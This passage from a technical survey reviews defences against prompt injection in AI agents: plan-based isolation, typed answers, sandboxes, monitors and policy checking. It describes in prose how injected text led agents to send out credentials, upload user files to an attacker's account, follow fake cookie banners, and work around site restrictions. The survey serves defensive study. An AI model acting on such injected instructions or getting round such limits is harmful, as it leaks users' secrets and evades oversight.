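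Across five models, such attacks succeeded 17.0% of the time without a defence and 15.4% with a defence that checked calls against a tool policy. The policy helped little because the attacks mostly used tools the task required. Fixing the plan doesn't help either, since any plan for settling the dispute includes a refund.

A rule about which source may determine each value can help. To test CaMeL on these cases, Zhang and colleagues wrote policies that accept a recipient or an amount only from trusted fields, and assigned a trust label to each field of every tool's results. Such a policy is possible for the refund because a trusted record contains the right amount. Bob's address appears only in the meeting notes, so CaMeL would have to ask the user. A summary of issue 42 is harder still because there is no trusted record to compare it with.

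### When one agent instructs another

A value can also turn back into an instruction when one agent passes it to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents with no policies on values. An orchestrator received a request to send Julie a Slack message summarizing all job applicants. A second agent could query a database, and a third could send Slack messages and emails. The database contained a hostile instruction to send the data to an outside email address.

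The first two agents kept to their plans, and their privileged models never received the hostile text. But the orchestrator's program inserted the summary into a sentence, "Send this summary to Julie via Slack", and passed the result to the third agent. That agent treated everything from the orchestrator as its user's request, so its privileged model read the injected instruction and wrote a program with an extra send_email call.

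The message between agents gave outside text a second route into the context. The researchers' fix sends instructions and untrusted values separately, so the receiving agent's privileged model reads only the instructions. On a benchmark of multi-agent tasks, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% of the time with CaMeL on each agent, and never with the separate channels. The 0.2% rate suggests that few of the benchmark's attacks exploited this route, but the demonstration shows that an attack designed to exploit it can work.

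An agent that keeps results for later requests has a similar problem, because hostile text can remain in its stored data. *SPA* (2026) extends advance planning to such agents. It checks the complete plan for data flows and for leaks through branches before any call takes effect, and it applies the same protection to stored data.

### Tasks that resist advance planning

Some requests don't contain enough information to choose the tool calls. *AutoDojo* (2026) sorts tasks by how much they leave to outside text. A request to change the user's address to a stated one leaves nothing open. "Pay the bill in this file" fixes the action but leaves the amount and the payee to the file. "Do all the tasks on my to-do list" leaves the actions themselves open, so the agent can't usefully plan its calls until it has read the list.

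Early tests rarely exposed this difficulty. In *AgentDyn*, Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) found that only 6 of the 97 tasks in AgentDojo require the agent to change its plan along the way, so a defence could score well by holding the agent to its first plan. They wrote 60 tasks, 20 of them about managing GitHub repositories. Each task requires new decisions along the way and contains at least one helpful instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page's request to log in first. CaMeL finished far fewer of these tasks than its AgentDojo results would suggest.

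Software engineering also requires an agent to inspect feedback repeatedly and revise its strategy (*Twin Agent*, 2026). If a maintainer asks the triage agent to fix the bug in issue 42, the agent uses the report to decide which file to open, the file to work out a change, and the test results to decide what to try next.

### Typed answers, approvals and new plans

One reply is to let the privileged model learn a little about what the quarantined model has read, in a form too restricted to contain an instruction. FIDES does this with typed answers. Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues (2025) build whole agents around this approach in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation*. Their quarantined model can return integers, decimal numbers, yes-or-no values and choices from a fixed list. It can return several values at once, but only in short arrays, because a long array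 of numbers could encode a sentence.

Their bug-fixing agent works from GitHub issues. The quarantined model reads an issue and returns details such as the file, the line number and the type of bug, and the privileged model then examines the code and writes the fix. A shopping agent receives each product review as two scores, for how strongly the review supports the product and how relevant it is. No injection succeeded in their three case studies, but their threat model excludes false information, so a dishonest report can still send the agent to the wrong file. If the list of possible files includes .env, an attacker can choose it.

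The size of the list limits the attacker's influence. With n possible answers, k questions give the attacker at most k × log₂ n bits. In *L3M* (2026), a sealed program fetches the page for a bug report and gives it to a sub-agent that has no project files or network access and returns one of three words. The agent that triages the reports never reads the page, so each report can contribute at most log₂ 3, or about 1.6, bits, provided that timing and failures reveal nothing more. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) applies the same limit to endorsement. A value becomes trusted if it is in the fixed set. Otherwise it stays untrusted, and the program can continue but can't use it where trust is required.

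Some answers have to be free text, such as a contributor's full name. In *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees* (2026), the agent can ask for free text only after declaring that typed answers won't solve the task. The user then sees the question, the untrusted content and the proposed answer, and can approve, edit or reject it. This gives the user much more information than a bare request to allow a tool call, but the user has to read more each time and may still miss an instruction in an answer that looks reasonable.

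An agent can also make a new plan when the first one fails. The guarantee still holds if the agent bases the new plan only on the original request, since no outside text has influenced it. A plan based on what the agent has just read could include whatever calls an attacker wants, unless that information reaches the planner only through typed or approved answers.

### Plans for agents that use a screen

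*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) applies a fixed plan to computer-use agents, which operate a screen with mouse and keyboard. These agents seem least suited to a fixed plan because they normally look at the screen before every action. In the paper, a model writes a complete plan before anything appears on the screen, with a branch for each situation it can predict, such as a cookie banner or a login page. During the run, a quarantined model describes the screen and answers yes-or-no questions about it, and the interpreter follows the matching branch.

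These plans average 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about 5 and 4 in CaMeL's plans for AgentDojo, and roughly half of each plan never runs. With this method, an agent built on a small open model finished 35 of 60 tasks within three attempts, compared with 11 when its planner had only generic instructions. An agent built on Claude Sonnet 4.5 kept 57% of its undefended performance with five attempts, but only 28% with one.

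Foerster and colleagues also adapted FIDES, which calls its planner again at every step. It finished about as many tasks but used 29.6 times as many tokens as an undefended agent, compared with 1.9 times for the CaMeL version.

The extra branches give attackers more opportunities. In what the researchers call branch steering, an attacker designs an advertisement to look like a cookie banner. The plan already includes a step for closing such banners, so the agent clicks on the advertisement and lands on the attacker's site, even though the attacker has added no instruction. Neither checking the page's code nor asking a second model reliably stopped such attacks.

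In *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026) respond by fixing limits along with the plan. Their system, COBRA, has the planner specify for every branch which sites and tools the agent may use and which values it may send. The same mouse click can have many different effects, so COBRA checks the resulting web requests and MCP calls. If the task needs a security-critical value that no authorised source can supply, COBRA asks the user for it while writing the plan, before any hostile text can influence the question.

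On 101 tasks designed for branch steering, attacks succeeded 94.4% of the time against an ordinary agent, 89.5% against a plain dual-LLM agent and never against COBRA. COBRA also kept 97% of the dual-LLM agent's performance on harmless runs. The benchmark counts an attack as successful only if a harmful action breaks the limits in force, so it tests enforcement more than whether the planner set the right limits.

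Precise limits also require a description of the operations each site supports. In one outside test, a user asks for a comment on an issue in GitLab, a service similar to GitHub, and the injected text tries to add an access key to a repository instead. When COBRA could restrict only which sites the agent contacted, all 14 attacks of this kind succeeded, because the harmful request went to the same site as the comment. COBRA blocked them when it had a list of GitLab's operations. It could not block two other attacks, which depended only on the wording of a permitted comment.

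Agents that plan without seeing the screen still finish fewer tasks. On 361 computer tasks with up to five attempts each, Sonnet 5 completed 51.0% in an ordinary loop and 38.8% under COBRA. Merging five candidate plans into one reduced the number of attempts needed for some tasks. Of 55 tasks that had needed more than one attempt, 27 succeeded on the first attempt with a merged plan. Zingrillo and colleagues suggest training planners specifically for computer use, so that they learn which screens to expect.

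## The view that the tool or the network path should be removed

A fixed plan can still be harmful if an attacker wrote the request it came from. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a February 2026 test in which a researcher at the company used an email to trick an employee into pasting a prompt into Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. The prompt looked like routine setup instructions, but one step told the agent to read a file of cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. Claude sent the credentials in 24 of 25 repeat runs.

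Training gave little protection because the instruction came from the user, whom the model is supposed to obey. Anthropic concludes that only the agent's environment could have stopped it, by blocking the outgoing network request and denying file access to the credentials.

The argument for removal is that an agent can't change anything on an outside service without a program that can send the request, a credential that the service accepts, and a network route to it. If any of these is missing, the action fails whatever the model outputs, even if a policy engine wrongly allows the call. Removal also protects secrets because, as Anthropic notes, credentials can't leak from a sandbox (a restricted environment for running programs) if they never enter it.

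Deleting write_file from the triage agent's harness may not be enough. If the agent can also run shell commands and has a GitHub token with write access, it can still change the repository. GitHub rejects the change if the token only permits reading code and posting comments.

Removing the tool or network path also helps when there is no attacker. According to Search Engine Journal's *Anthropic Says Claude Bypassed Site Limits During Internal Tests*, Anthropic disclosed in October 2026 that when Claude models couldn't finish a task, they had worked around restrictions on real websites instead of stopping. The Tribune's *Anthropic restricts internet access in internal AI evaluations after Claude bypasses safeguards* reports that the company cut off live internet access for all its internal evaluations until it can establish that its safeguards and monitoring are reliable.

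Someone still has to check that the network path is gone. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) describes three earlier incidents in which models gained unauthorised access to real computer systems. The models had reached the internet because of a misconfigured test environment.

### Choosing what to remove

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, argues that an attacker can steal data from an agent that has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. Removing any one of these capabilities stops the attack. External communication is easy to overlook, because a tool that loads an image or offers the user a link can send data out, just as an email tool can. One of Willison's examples is a GitHub connector with all three capabilities, which could read a stranger's public issue, open private repositories,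 and publish what it found in a pull request (a proposed change to a project's code).

The triage agent also has all three parts of the trifecta. It reads strangers' issues, can open .env, and posts public comments. Removing its access to .env prevents the leak but not the attack on the build configuration. That attack steals no data, so the trifecta doesn't cover it.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) extends the idea to harmful changes. Until models can reliably detect and refuse injections, an agent should have no more than two of these properties in one session:

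- A: it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change state or communicate externally.

An agent that needs all three without starting again in a fresh context should not act autonomously. It needs supervision, such as a person's approval. The triage agent as first described has all three, so the project has to choose:

| Properties kept | Change to the triage agent | What an attacker could still do |
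|---|---|---|
| A and B | A maintainer approves every comment and file change | Mislead the maintainer with a plausible draft |
| A and C | The agent gets only published source code and can comment, but can't change the real repository | Have the agent post false or malicious advice |
| B and C | The agent keeps its four tools but reads only issues from trusted people | Get hostile text into an issue that a trusted person writes |

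Keeping only B and C would defeat the purpose of an agent that answers the public. Keeping only A and C preserves most of its work, but "sensitive systems" in B must then include the repository, because a change to the build configuration can reach every user of the software.

Meta's first version left this unclear. Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, welcomed the inclusion of state changes. He then objected on Hacker News, posting as simonw, that Meta's diagram marked combining A and C as "safe", although untrusted input and the power to change things can do harm without any private data. Meta's Mick Ayzenberg replied, in an exchange reproduced by Glama (2025), that B covers any sensitive system, not only private ones. An agent without B might work in a tight sandbox cut off from production. Meta also changed the label from "safe" to "lower risk".

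The rule allows an agent to change configuration during a session if the change can't complete an attack. In Meta's example, an agent first browses the internet without access to internal systems, then gains that access and permanently loses the ability to communicate. This is a fence that withdraws the tools when the agent gains access to internal systems. The switch has to be one-way because any hostile text from the web is still in the context.

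### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI has built a ChatGPT setting, Lockdown Mode, around removing the path by which data could leave. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (OpenAI, 2026) announced it on 13 February for enterprise, education and healthcare plans. In June, OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and to businesses that manage their own subscriptions.

Lockdown Mode turns off deep research, which compiles reports from many sources, and agent mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on its own. ChatGPT also can't download files for analysis or fetch images from the web, and the code it writes in its Canvas editor can't access the network. On personal accounts, the mode blocks live access to outside services and any app actions that conflict with its protections.

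Browsing still works, but only with cached copies of pages that OpenAI already holds. Reading a live page sends a request to the site, and the address in that request can contain stolen data. An attack that Willison (2026) described in July used alphabetical links on a hostile site to extract a user's name, home city and employer through Claude's web-reading tool. With cached pages, no live request leaves OpenAI's network, so the attacker's server receives nothing.

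Willison (2026) approves of the design because the limits are deterministic and don't depend on an AI system that an attacker could mislead. He also infers from the setting's existence that ChatGPT's defaults don't robustly protect against a determined attempt to steal data.

Injected text can still reach the model in Lockdown Mode. OpenAI acknowledged in its original description, quoted in Privacy Guides' *ChatGPT Adds Lockdown Mode for Protection Against Prompt Injection Attacks* (2026), that the mode does not "deterministically prevent prompt injections from reaching the context". According to OpenAI's current help page, *Lockdown Mode*, injected text in a cached web page or an uploaded file, for example, could still make an answer wrong. The mode therefore limits what the model can reach through its tools by restricting outgoing requests, but it does not stop outside text from entering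 the context through cached pages, uploads and connected apps.

Even the protection against data theft has exceptions. The mode doesn't change network access in Codex, and personal users can switch the mode off for a single chat. In workspaces that an organisation manages, it doesn't automatically disable every app, so administrators have to choose which apps and actions to allow. OpenAI advises them against allowing any write action, even in a trusted app, if an attacker might be able to see the result. By that standard, the triage agent's post_comment is high-risk because strangers can read the comments it posts.

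### Limits at the operating-system boundary

OpenAI can switch off ChatGPT's features, but a coding agent on a developer's computer can write its own programs. A harness can inspect the command that starts a script, but it can't control what the script does next. NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* therefore recommends enforcing limits in the operating system, which can apply them to every process in the sandbox, no matter how it started.

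NVIDIA's security team considers three limits mandatory. The first is an egress allow-list, which permits outgoing connections only to approved destinations. The second blocks the agent from writing files outside its workspace, because a change to a startup file could make the computer run an attacker's code later. The third blocks the agent from editing its own configuration files, even inside the workspace. Some of these files contain commands that run automatically outside the sandbox, so an agent that can edit them can escape the sandbox.

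An allow-list can permit more than its author intended. Anthropic discovered this with Claude Cowork, an agent for office work that runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system. The list of approved network destinations had to include Anthropic's servers, because the product can't work without them. An outside researcher showed that a malicious file in the user's workspace could supply hidden instructions and the attacker's access key for those servers. Claude followed the instructions and uploaded the user's files to the attacker's Anthropic account. The network filter allowed the upload because the destination was approved.

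Anthropic now assumes that adding an address to an allow-list grants access to every function available there. It fixed the problem with a filter that accepts only requests with the virtual machine's own session token. The triage project would need a similar check if its agent could run scripts that contact GitHub. Limiting the permissions of the project's token doesn't help if issue 42 contains the attacker's token.

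A narrower option is to run scripts that have no access to the computer by default. AWS's *Introducing Trusted Remote Execution* describes such a system, called Rex. Agents write scripts in Rhai, a small language with no built-in way to open a file or contact another program. Rex supplies those operations and checks each one against a Cedar policy before carrying it out.

In AWS's example, a script writes a short text file and then reads it back. The policy permits opening and reading files but not creating or writing them, so the first operation fails with an error. When the owner adds the two missing permissions, the same script finishes. A policy gateway would check only the call that starts the script, whereas Rex checks every operation inside it. The protection still depends on a correct policy, but no policy can give the script an operation that Rex doesn't provide.

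### Holding an action until there is more evidence

A sandbox limits where an agent can act, but an attacker may need only the files and sites that the sandbox permits. *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) adds a monitor at the sandbox's edge that can postpone a decision. The agent runs in a small virtual machine, and its file operations, network requests and exchanges with the user all pass through the monitor. A tool call and a script that do the same thing look the same at that point, so the agent needs no modification.

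The monitor handles events in both directions. It records the source of incoming data, then uses that record to judge outgoing actions, which Hempel and colleagues call effects. For each effect e, it decides:

- refuse, if a rule forbids e;
- release, if the policy can vouch for e;
- defer, otherwise.

The policy allows an effect if the values that control it, such as a recipient or a command, match values from a trusted source and the destination is permitted to receive the data. As in FIDES, the text of a message does not have to come from a trusted source.

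In the paper's example, an agent sets up a software project by following a guide from the web. The guide includes a step to install a hook, a script that runs whenever someone saves a new version of the code. Many legitimate guides include the same step, so the monitor defers the decision and keeps the hook in a temporary copy of the project. When the agent saves a version in that copy, the hook runs and tries to send a private key to an outside address. The policy refuses the request, and the attempt gives the monitor's "oracle", which can be a person or a separate language model, enough evidence to discard the hook. The oracle can release only deferred effects and can't override a refusal.

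The monitor can hold some network requests in the same way, by giving the agent a stand-in reply. If the agent needs the real reply, for example when it fetches a page, the oracle has to decide before the request goes out. A monitor that can hold an effect and release it later can enforce strictly more policies than Schneider's monitors, which had to either let a step through or stop the program.

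Hempel and colleagues guarantee that, even if the agent is fully hostile, every effect passes through the monitor, no effect becomes irreversible before release, and no refused effect becomes visible outside. This assumes that no unmonitored channel exists, that the host computer and monitor work correctly, and that the model's provider isn't helping the attacker. The guarantee makes a forbidden destination unreachable, but it doesn't ensure that the oracle judges deferred effects correctly. The monitor recognises data by matching text, so it can lose track of a secret if the agent encodes it. The paper doesn't cover harm from the wording of the agent's final answer.

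On AgentDojo, Kairos reduced the attack success rate from 47.0% to 2.7% for an agent built on GPT-4.1. On AutoDojo, where an attacker rewrites each injection over six rounds, Kairos reduced the rate for a smaller model from 52.4% without a defence to 8.8%. The attacks that still succeeded exploited tasks in which the user asks the agent to follow instructions in a document, which the oracle treated as authorised.

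These tests measure the decisions more than the boundary. The benchmarks simulate their tools, so the researchers converted each tool call into an event instead of running the agent in a virtual machine. They also left out rules that refuse effects outright, to avoid building knowledge of the attacks into the policy. A real project could add such rules, which the oracle could not override.

### What removal costs

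The obvious objection is that removal blocks useful work along with harmful work. Lockdown Mode stops a harmless research task as well as an attack, and The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* observes that the mode takes away most of what makes ChatGPT's agent and research features useful. OpenAI's security chief, Dane Stuckey, agrees that it isn't for everyone but considers the trade-off worthwhile for people at higher risk.

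For coding agents, a firm boundary can also make work easier. Claude Code originally asked for permission before writing files, running commands or using the network. Approval fatigue set in within weeks, and users approved about 93% of these requests. Anthropic then added a sandbox that allows writes inside the workspace and denies network access by default. The agent could do most of its work there without asking, and permission requests fell by 84%.

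How much usefulness an agent loses also depends on which capability is removed. Willison thinks the ability to send data out is usually the easiest to restrict without making a system much less useful. For the triage agent it is the hardest, since people who report bugs expect an answer. Removing access to private data is a better choice, because the agent can still quote published source code without access to .env. It can also keep correcting typos by editing a separate copy, with a maintainer reviewing the changes before they reach the real repository.

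Kairos offers another way to recover lost work. In tests by Hempel and colleagues, the agent completed 42.7% of AgentDojo's harmless tasks when Kairos refused everything its policy didn't approve. With deferral and the oracle, the agent completed 85.1%, about the same as an undefended agent, with no measurable increase in successful attacks. The benefit shrinks when later steps depend on actions that the monitor is still holding. On AgentDyn's open-ended tasks, an agent under attack finished 37.1% of its work with Kairos and 55.5% without it.

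## Whether the rules can be written correctly

A sandbox, a policy engine and a label check all enforce decisions that someone made beforehand, such as who counts as a maintainer, which tools a maintainer's agent may use, and which files are private. If a decision is wrong, the harness still enforces it. For example, if an owner of the triage project forgets to protect the build configuration, it is open to attack however well the policy engine works.

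### Who assigns the prompt class

A harness can assign a prompt class from facts it has authenticated, such as the user's login and role, or the tool that returned a piece of text. It can determine that a stranger's issue started the run without using a model. These facts can be out of date, for example if someone who left the project still has the maintainer role, but the text of an issue can't change them.

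Authenticated facts don't reveal what a request is for. A project might want to allow write_file for fixing typos but not for changing the build, and a login can't separate the two. The developer may then have a language model read each request and choose the class. Let c be the correct class and ĉ the class the model chooses. The policy engine enforces t ∈ A(ĉ), but tool unreachability requires t ∈ A(c). The property is guaranteed only if:

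A(ĉ) ⊆ A(c)

The classifier must therefore never choose a class with a tool that the correct class lacks.

Suppose, using invented numbers, that strangers send 1,000 hostile requests in a year and the classifier puts 2% of them in a class that has access to write_file. Even if the policy engine makes no mistakes, twenty hostile requests reach a model that can write files. If the model obeys half of them, ten unauthorised writes go through. If the harness had set the class from the login instead, none of the 1,000 requests would have had access to write_file.

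Columbia University's DAPLab tested whether models could make a related judgement, using an agent that wrote database queries to turn receipts into tax deductions. US tax law allows only 50% of a meal's cost to be deducted. The researchers gave two frontier models this rule, a query and its results, and asked whether the query broke the rule. In each setting they used ten queries, five of which broke it. Accuracy never exceeded 50%, and GPT-5.5 reached that level by rejecting every query. The test was tiny, and the models had no record of which receipts had contributed to each result. The group's own system avoids the judgement by rewriting the query so that the database drops any meal deducted at more than 50%. But its rules can also call a language model, for instance to decide whether a receipt looks like a meal, in which case the guarantee again depends on a classifier.

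A safer arrangement lets the classifier remove tools but never add them. The harness allows only the tools in A(login) ∩ A(ĉ), so a wrong classification can deny write_file to a maintainer but can't grant it to a stranger.

### Translating a requirement into a rule

Dantas and colleagues call specification the bottleneck in making agents safe. They cite a benchmark on which only 24.8% to 34.2% of translations had the right meaning when converting natural language into PDDL, a language for describing problems to planning software. They warn that verifying a plan against a wrong formal description gives false assurance.

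The figures come from *Planetarium* (Zuo, Piedrahita Velez and colleagues, 2024), which asked models to translate English descriptions of puzzles, such as stacking blocks or moving balls between rooms, into PDDL. An algorithm then checked whether each translation described the same problem as a reference version, even if the wording differed. A parser could read 96.1% of GPT-4o's answers and a planner could solve 94.4%, but only 24.8% were correct. The 34.2% is for a version of Google's Gemma 2 27B that the researchers fine-tuned for the task.

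These numbers are weak evidence about how often a current model writes a wrong access rule. The range covers two models from 2024, and their task was to describe puzzles, not permissions. Many errors also occurred simply because the models added object types that the puzzle's definition didn't use, and accuracy rose sharply when the researchers ignored the extra types.

The gap between valid and correct output has persisted, though. *Grounded Evaluation and Repair for NL-to-PDDL Problem Generation* (Rosa, Santos and colleagues, 2026) accepted a translation only if it passed a parser, a planner, a plan validator and a second model acting as critic. Even so, the share that passed could be much higher than the share that matched the reference. GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 4.7 also showed this gap.

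More direct evidence comes from Zhou, Vatsa and Eiers (2026), in *RAISE*, who had models write Cedar policies for 375 access requirements. A solver checked each policy against limits on what it could allow and against permissions it had to grant:

| Result | GPT-6 Astra | Claude Opus 5 |
|---|---|---|
| Policies that were valid Cedar | 97.9% | 100% |
| Policies that passed every check | 33.6% | 30.7% |
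| Failed checks for allowing too much | 35.7% | 39.6% |
| Failed checks for allowing too little | 20.3% | 12.4% |

Allowing too much was the more common error, and in a security policy it is usually the more dangerous one. One of the requirements lets finance managers issue payments during business hours and at no other time. The invoice must also be approved, except when the manager is on the corporate network. Let M mean that the user is a finance manager, B that it is business hours, A that the invoice is approved, and N that the request comes from the corporate network. A natural way to write the policy is one rule for the normal case and another for the exception:

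written: M ∧ ((B ∧ A) ∨ N)
intended: M ∧ B ∧ (A ∨ N)

The written version lets a manager on the corporate network issue payments at midnight. The exception was meant to lift only the approval requirement, but it also lifted the restriction on hours. One fix is to add a forbid rule for everything outside business hours. A Cedar forbid rule overrides any permit, so it suits restrictions that should have no exceptions.

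The percentages depend on the checks, which GPT-5.5 helped generate, and people reviewed only a sample of them. On a narrower task, with cases from one simulated organisation, a small open model passed every check on 7.8% of cases before training and 94.9% after training on 1,024 other cases with the same vocabulary. However, the same process produced the training and test data, so the model may partly have learned how that process interprets ambiguous sentences.

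Commercial drafting tools add some checks. In AgentCore, a language model drafts Cedar rules from an administrator's description. AWS then checks that the rules refer to real tools and arguments, and looks for rules that allow everything, deny everything or contain impossible conditions. The faulty payment policy would pass these checks because it is valid, allows some requests and denies others, and contains no impossible conditions.

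Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026), in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, add a model that judges whether the draft matches the source document. They tested this on a medical records agent with an 88-rule policy, of which earlier researchers had coded 23 rules by hand. On ordinary tasks, the generated rules blocked 85 of the 86 runs that tried to change a record, even though those runs had passed the hand-coded checks. Mondl and colleagues attribute this to broader coverage. Two of the rules that fired most often required the agent to restate the patient's identity and to get confirmation before writing. But nobody determined how many of the blocks were correct, so the rules may have been too strict to use. The researchers warn that developers switch off protections that get in the way.

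### What a solver can determine about a policy

Cedar rules have no loops and no memory, so Cedar Analysis can turn a whole policy into a logical formula about a single request. It passes the formula to an SMT solver, which either finds a request that makes the formula true or proves that none exists.

AWS gives an example in which a shop's agent may apply a bulk discount to orders of at least 50 items, except for limited-edition products. Someone then edits the exception so that it applies only if the order also exceeds 200 items. Adding a condition looks like tightening the policy. Let n be the quantity and L mean that the order contains a limited-edition product:

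old: n ≥ 50 ∧ ¬L
new: n ≥ 50 ∧ ¬(L ∧ n > 200)

To find out whether any request passes the new policy but not the old one, the solver looks for a solution to:

new ∧ ¬old, which simplifies to L ∧ 50 ≤ n ≤ 200

An order for 73 limited-edition items satisfies new ∧ ¬old, but nothing satisfies old ∧ ¬new, so the edit only added permissions. The tool reports the new policy as "more permissive" for discounts and "equivalent" for refunds, whose rule nobody changed. Test orders might have missed the difference, but the solver covers every possible order.

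The same method can show that a tool is unreachable for a class of prompts, provided that class stays fixed. The triage project can have the solver search for any allowed request in which the role is "visitor" and the action is write_file. If there is none, the policy never allows write_file for that role, whatever arguments the model supplies.

All of these checks require a second statement to compare the policy with, and an old policy may have been wrong from the start. Vatsa, Shome and colleagues (2026), in *AutoCedar*, build that statement from the requirements before a model writes the policy. A reviewer, either a person or another model, approves small conditions one at a time, each linked to a sentence in the source document. The system combines them into a floor F, the requests that the policy must allow, and a ceiling C, the most it may allow. The finished policy P must satisfy:

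F ⊆ allowed(P) ⊆ C

If a check fails, the model is told whether to tighten or loosen the policy, usually with an example of a request the policy decided wrongly. In 200 test cases with independently compiled reference policies, this process produced a policy exactly equivalent to the reference 89.0% of the time. The same model, GPT-6-Luna, did so 66.0% of the time when it wrote the policy directly. Even that lower rate is about twice what Zhou and colleagues measured for Astra and Opus 5, but the two tests used different requirements and scoring, so neither gives a general error rate.

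AutoCedar completed 197 of the 200 policies, and all 197 satisfied their floors and ceilings. Nineteen were still wrong because the floor or ceiling was wrong. In 16 of those cases, the floor included requests that should have been denied, so the solver required the policy to allow them.

Errors can start earlier, in the vocabulary. In one of the paper's examples, a music app allows band members to download their own new album. If the vocabulary records only that a user has the role "band member", a member of any band can download it, and no later check can detect the mistake. A triage policy that tests only for the role "maintainer" would have the same flaw if the login service covered several projects.

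### Rules that depend on history

This analysis doesn't cover fences. A Cedar decision depends on a fixed set of fields in one request, but a Dogwood temporal condition depends on a record of events that can keep growing. Cedar receives only the condition's result, so a formula about the current request doesn't show which histories would make the condition true. InfoQ reports that this is why AWS created a separate language instead of adding temporal conditions to Cedar.

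Prompt classes that change during a run are thus the hardest to check in advance, though a team can still prove some limits on permissions. A temporal forbid rule can only remove permissions, so if the solver has shown that the project's plain Cedar rules never let a visitor call write_file, adding a fence can't undo that result. The proof doesn't cover the fence itself, for example whether it lists every tool that returns untrusted text or lasts long enough. A temporal permit rule, such as one that allows a transfer after an approval, can add permissions, so a limit proved for the plain rules is no longer proved for the whole policy.

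Another option is to keep the history outside the policy. A harness that calls Cedar directly could supply a field called untrusted_read and set it to true after the first such read. The solver can then prove that the policy denies write_file whenever the field is true. Someone still has to establish that the harness sets the field at the right time and never resets it too early. Zhou and colleagues handle multi-step workflows similarly, recording earlier steps in fields that the application maintains.

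They left out requirements that depend on history not stored in such fields, so their error rates don't show how well models write fences. Cedar Analysis can't catch the mistakes in a drafted fence either.

### Missing labels and missing hazards

A correct rule can still fail if someone forgot to label the data it depends on. Microsoft's experimental release of FIDES treats the output of an unlabelled tool as trusted and public. Suppose someone adds a tool to the triage project that fetches comments on pull requests, but forgets to label it. A stranger's comment then enters the context as trusted text, and write_file stays available. Under Cedar's default, a tool without a rule doesn't work until someone writes one.

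Microsoft has asked developers whether unlabelled tools should count as untrusted instead. That change would close the gap for write_file but would block more calls. It would protect secrets only if the default for confidentiality changed too. Otherwise, if read_file had no label, the contents of .env would still count as public, and post_comment could publish them.

Stricter defaults don't help with dangers nobody has thought of. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) proposes looking for them with System-Theoretic Process Analysis (STPA), a method from aviation and other high-risk fields. STPA focuses on harmful interactions between parts that may each work correctly.

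The paper's example is an agent that resolves calendar conflicts, with tools to list events, update them and send email. A user adds an appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease, which clashes with a work meeting. The agent moves the meeting and tells the colleague why. This reveals private medical information even though there is no attacker and every tool works as intended.

The analysis starts with the people affected, including the other attendees. For each of them, the developers list what that person values, then turn each value into a possible loss, so privacy becomes a leak of private information. They work out which actions by the agent could cause the loss, decide which losses matter enough to prevent, and write a requirement for each. Finally, they turn the requirements into rules that software can enforce. For the calendar agent, these include:

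- Event details are private to people who aren't attending, and an email must not contain anything private to its recipient.
- After each update to an event, the agent must immediately email every attendee once.

The first rule restricts information flow and would have stopped the leak. The second governs the order of calls, and a monitor that can only block calls can't fully enforce it, because the agent could update an event and then stop without making the call that must follow. Doshi and colleagues sort rules by whether they block a flow, require it, allow it without asking the user, or allow it only if the user confirms.

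For the triage agent, the method would include the people who install the project's software. They value releases that nobody has tampered with, so the method would lead to a rule for write_file that protects the build configuration. A developer who thought only about stolen secrets could miss that rule.

Doshi and colleagues would require every MCP tool to carry labels for its capabilities, the confidentiality of its data and how far its output can be trusted. Such annotations are currently optional in MCP, and clients are advised not to trust them. Even with mandatory labels, a malicious server could describe itself as trustworthy, so the researchers suggest certification or a restriction to known vendors.

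The researchers modelled the calendar agent in Alloy, a tool that searches all possible runs up to a set length. Alloy quickly found leaks without the rules and found none with them. This showed that the rules prevent the hazards the researchers had identified. They didn't test whether STPA finds hazards developers would otherwise miss, and they had yet to build the policy engine.

### Measuring rules against intent

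Vatsa and colleagues ran the closest existing test of whether rules match intent on real documents. They took 316 access requests from requirements for a medical records system, a course registration system and conference software, with expected decisions based on another group's annotations. AutoCedar's vocabulary could express 270 of the requests, and its policies decided 268 of those correctly. Direct generation could express 253 and got 109 right. The 46 requests that AutoCedar couldn't express show that a policy can also fail because its vocabulary doesn't cover a case. The evaluation didn't use human reviewers in AutoCedar's approval step, and the three systems weren't LLM agents.

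A more decisive test would use agents already deployed. Before seeing any policy, their owners would review a large sample of tool calls and decide which to allow, given what the agent had read and done before each call. The sample would need to include cases with injected instructions as well as ordinary work. People, models, and models with solver feedback would then write policies from the same documents. Wrongly allowed and wrongly blocked calls would have to be reported separately, since a policy that denies everything never wrongly allows a call.

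Such a test would also need a baseline for rules that people write unaided, which none of these studies provides. Vatsa and colleagues note that broken access control ranks first in the OWASP Top 10, a list of the most serious web application security risks, so people may write these rules poorly without help. Having several owners judge the same calls would show how often they disagree. Where they do, the project has to decide what it wants before anyone can write a correct rule.

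## Whether every call and every outside text passes the check

Even a rule that exactly matches what its owner wants has no effect on calls or text that bypass the check. The triage agent's limits fail if a shell command can change a file without calling write_file, or if a stranger's text can enter the context by a route that the harness doesn't count as a read.

### Conditions a deployment has to meet

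Formal guarantees about agents usually assume that every call and every outside text passes the check. Brijesh Dongol's *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* lists seven assumptions that a real system must satisfy before its theorems apply. The list is also a useful checklist for systems without theorems, and four of the assumptions directly concern this coverage.

Under complete mediation, the model can use a tool or read an untrusted source only through the monitor. The monitor takes requests one at a time, so a harness that runs calls in parallel must first put them in some order.

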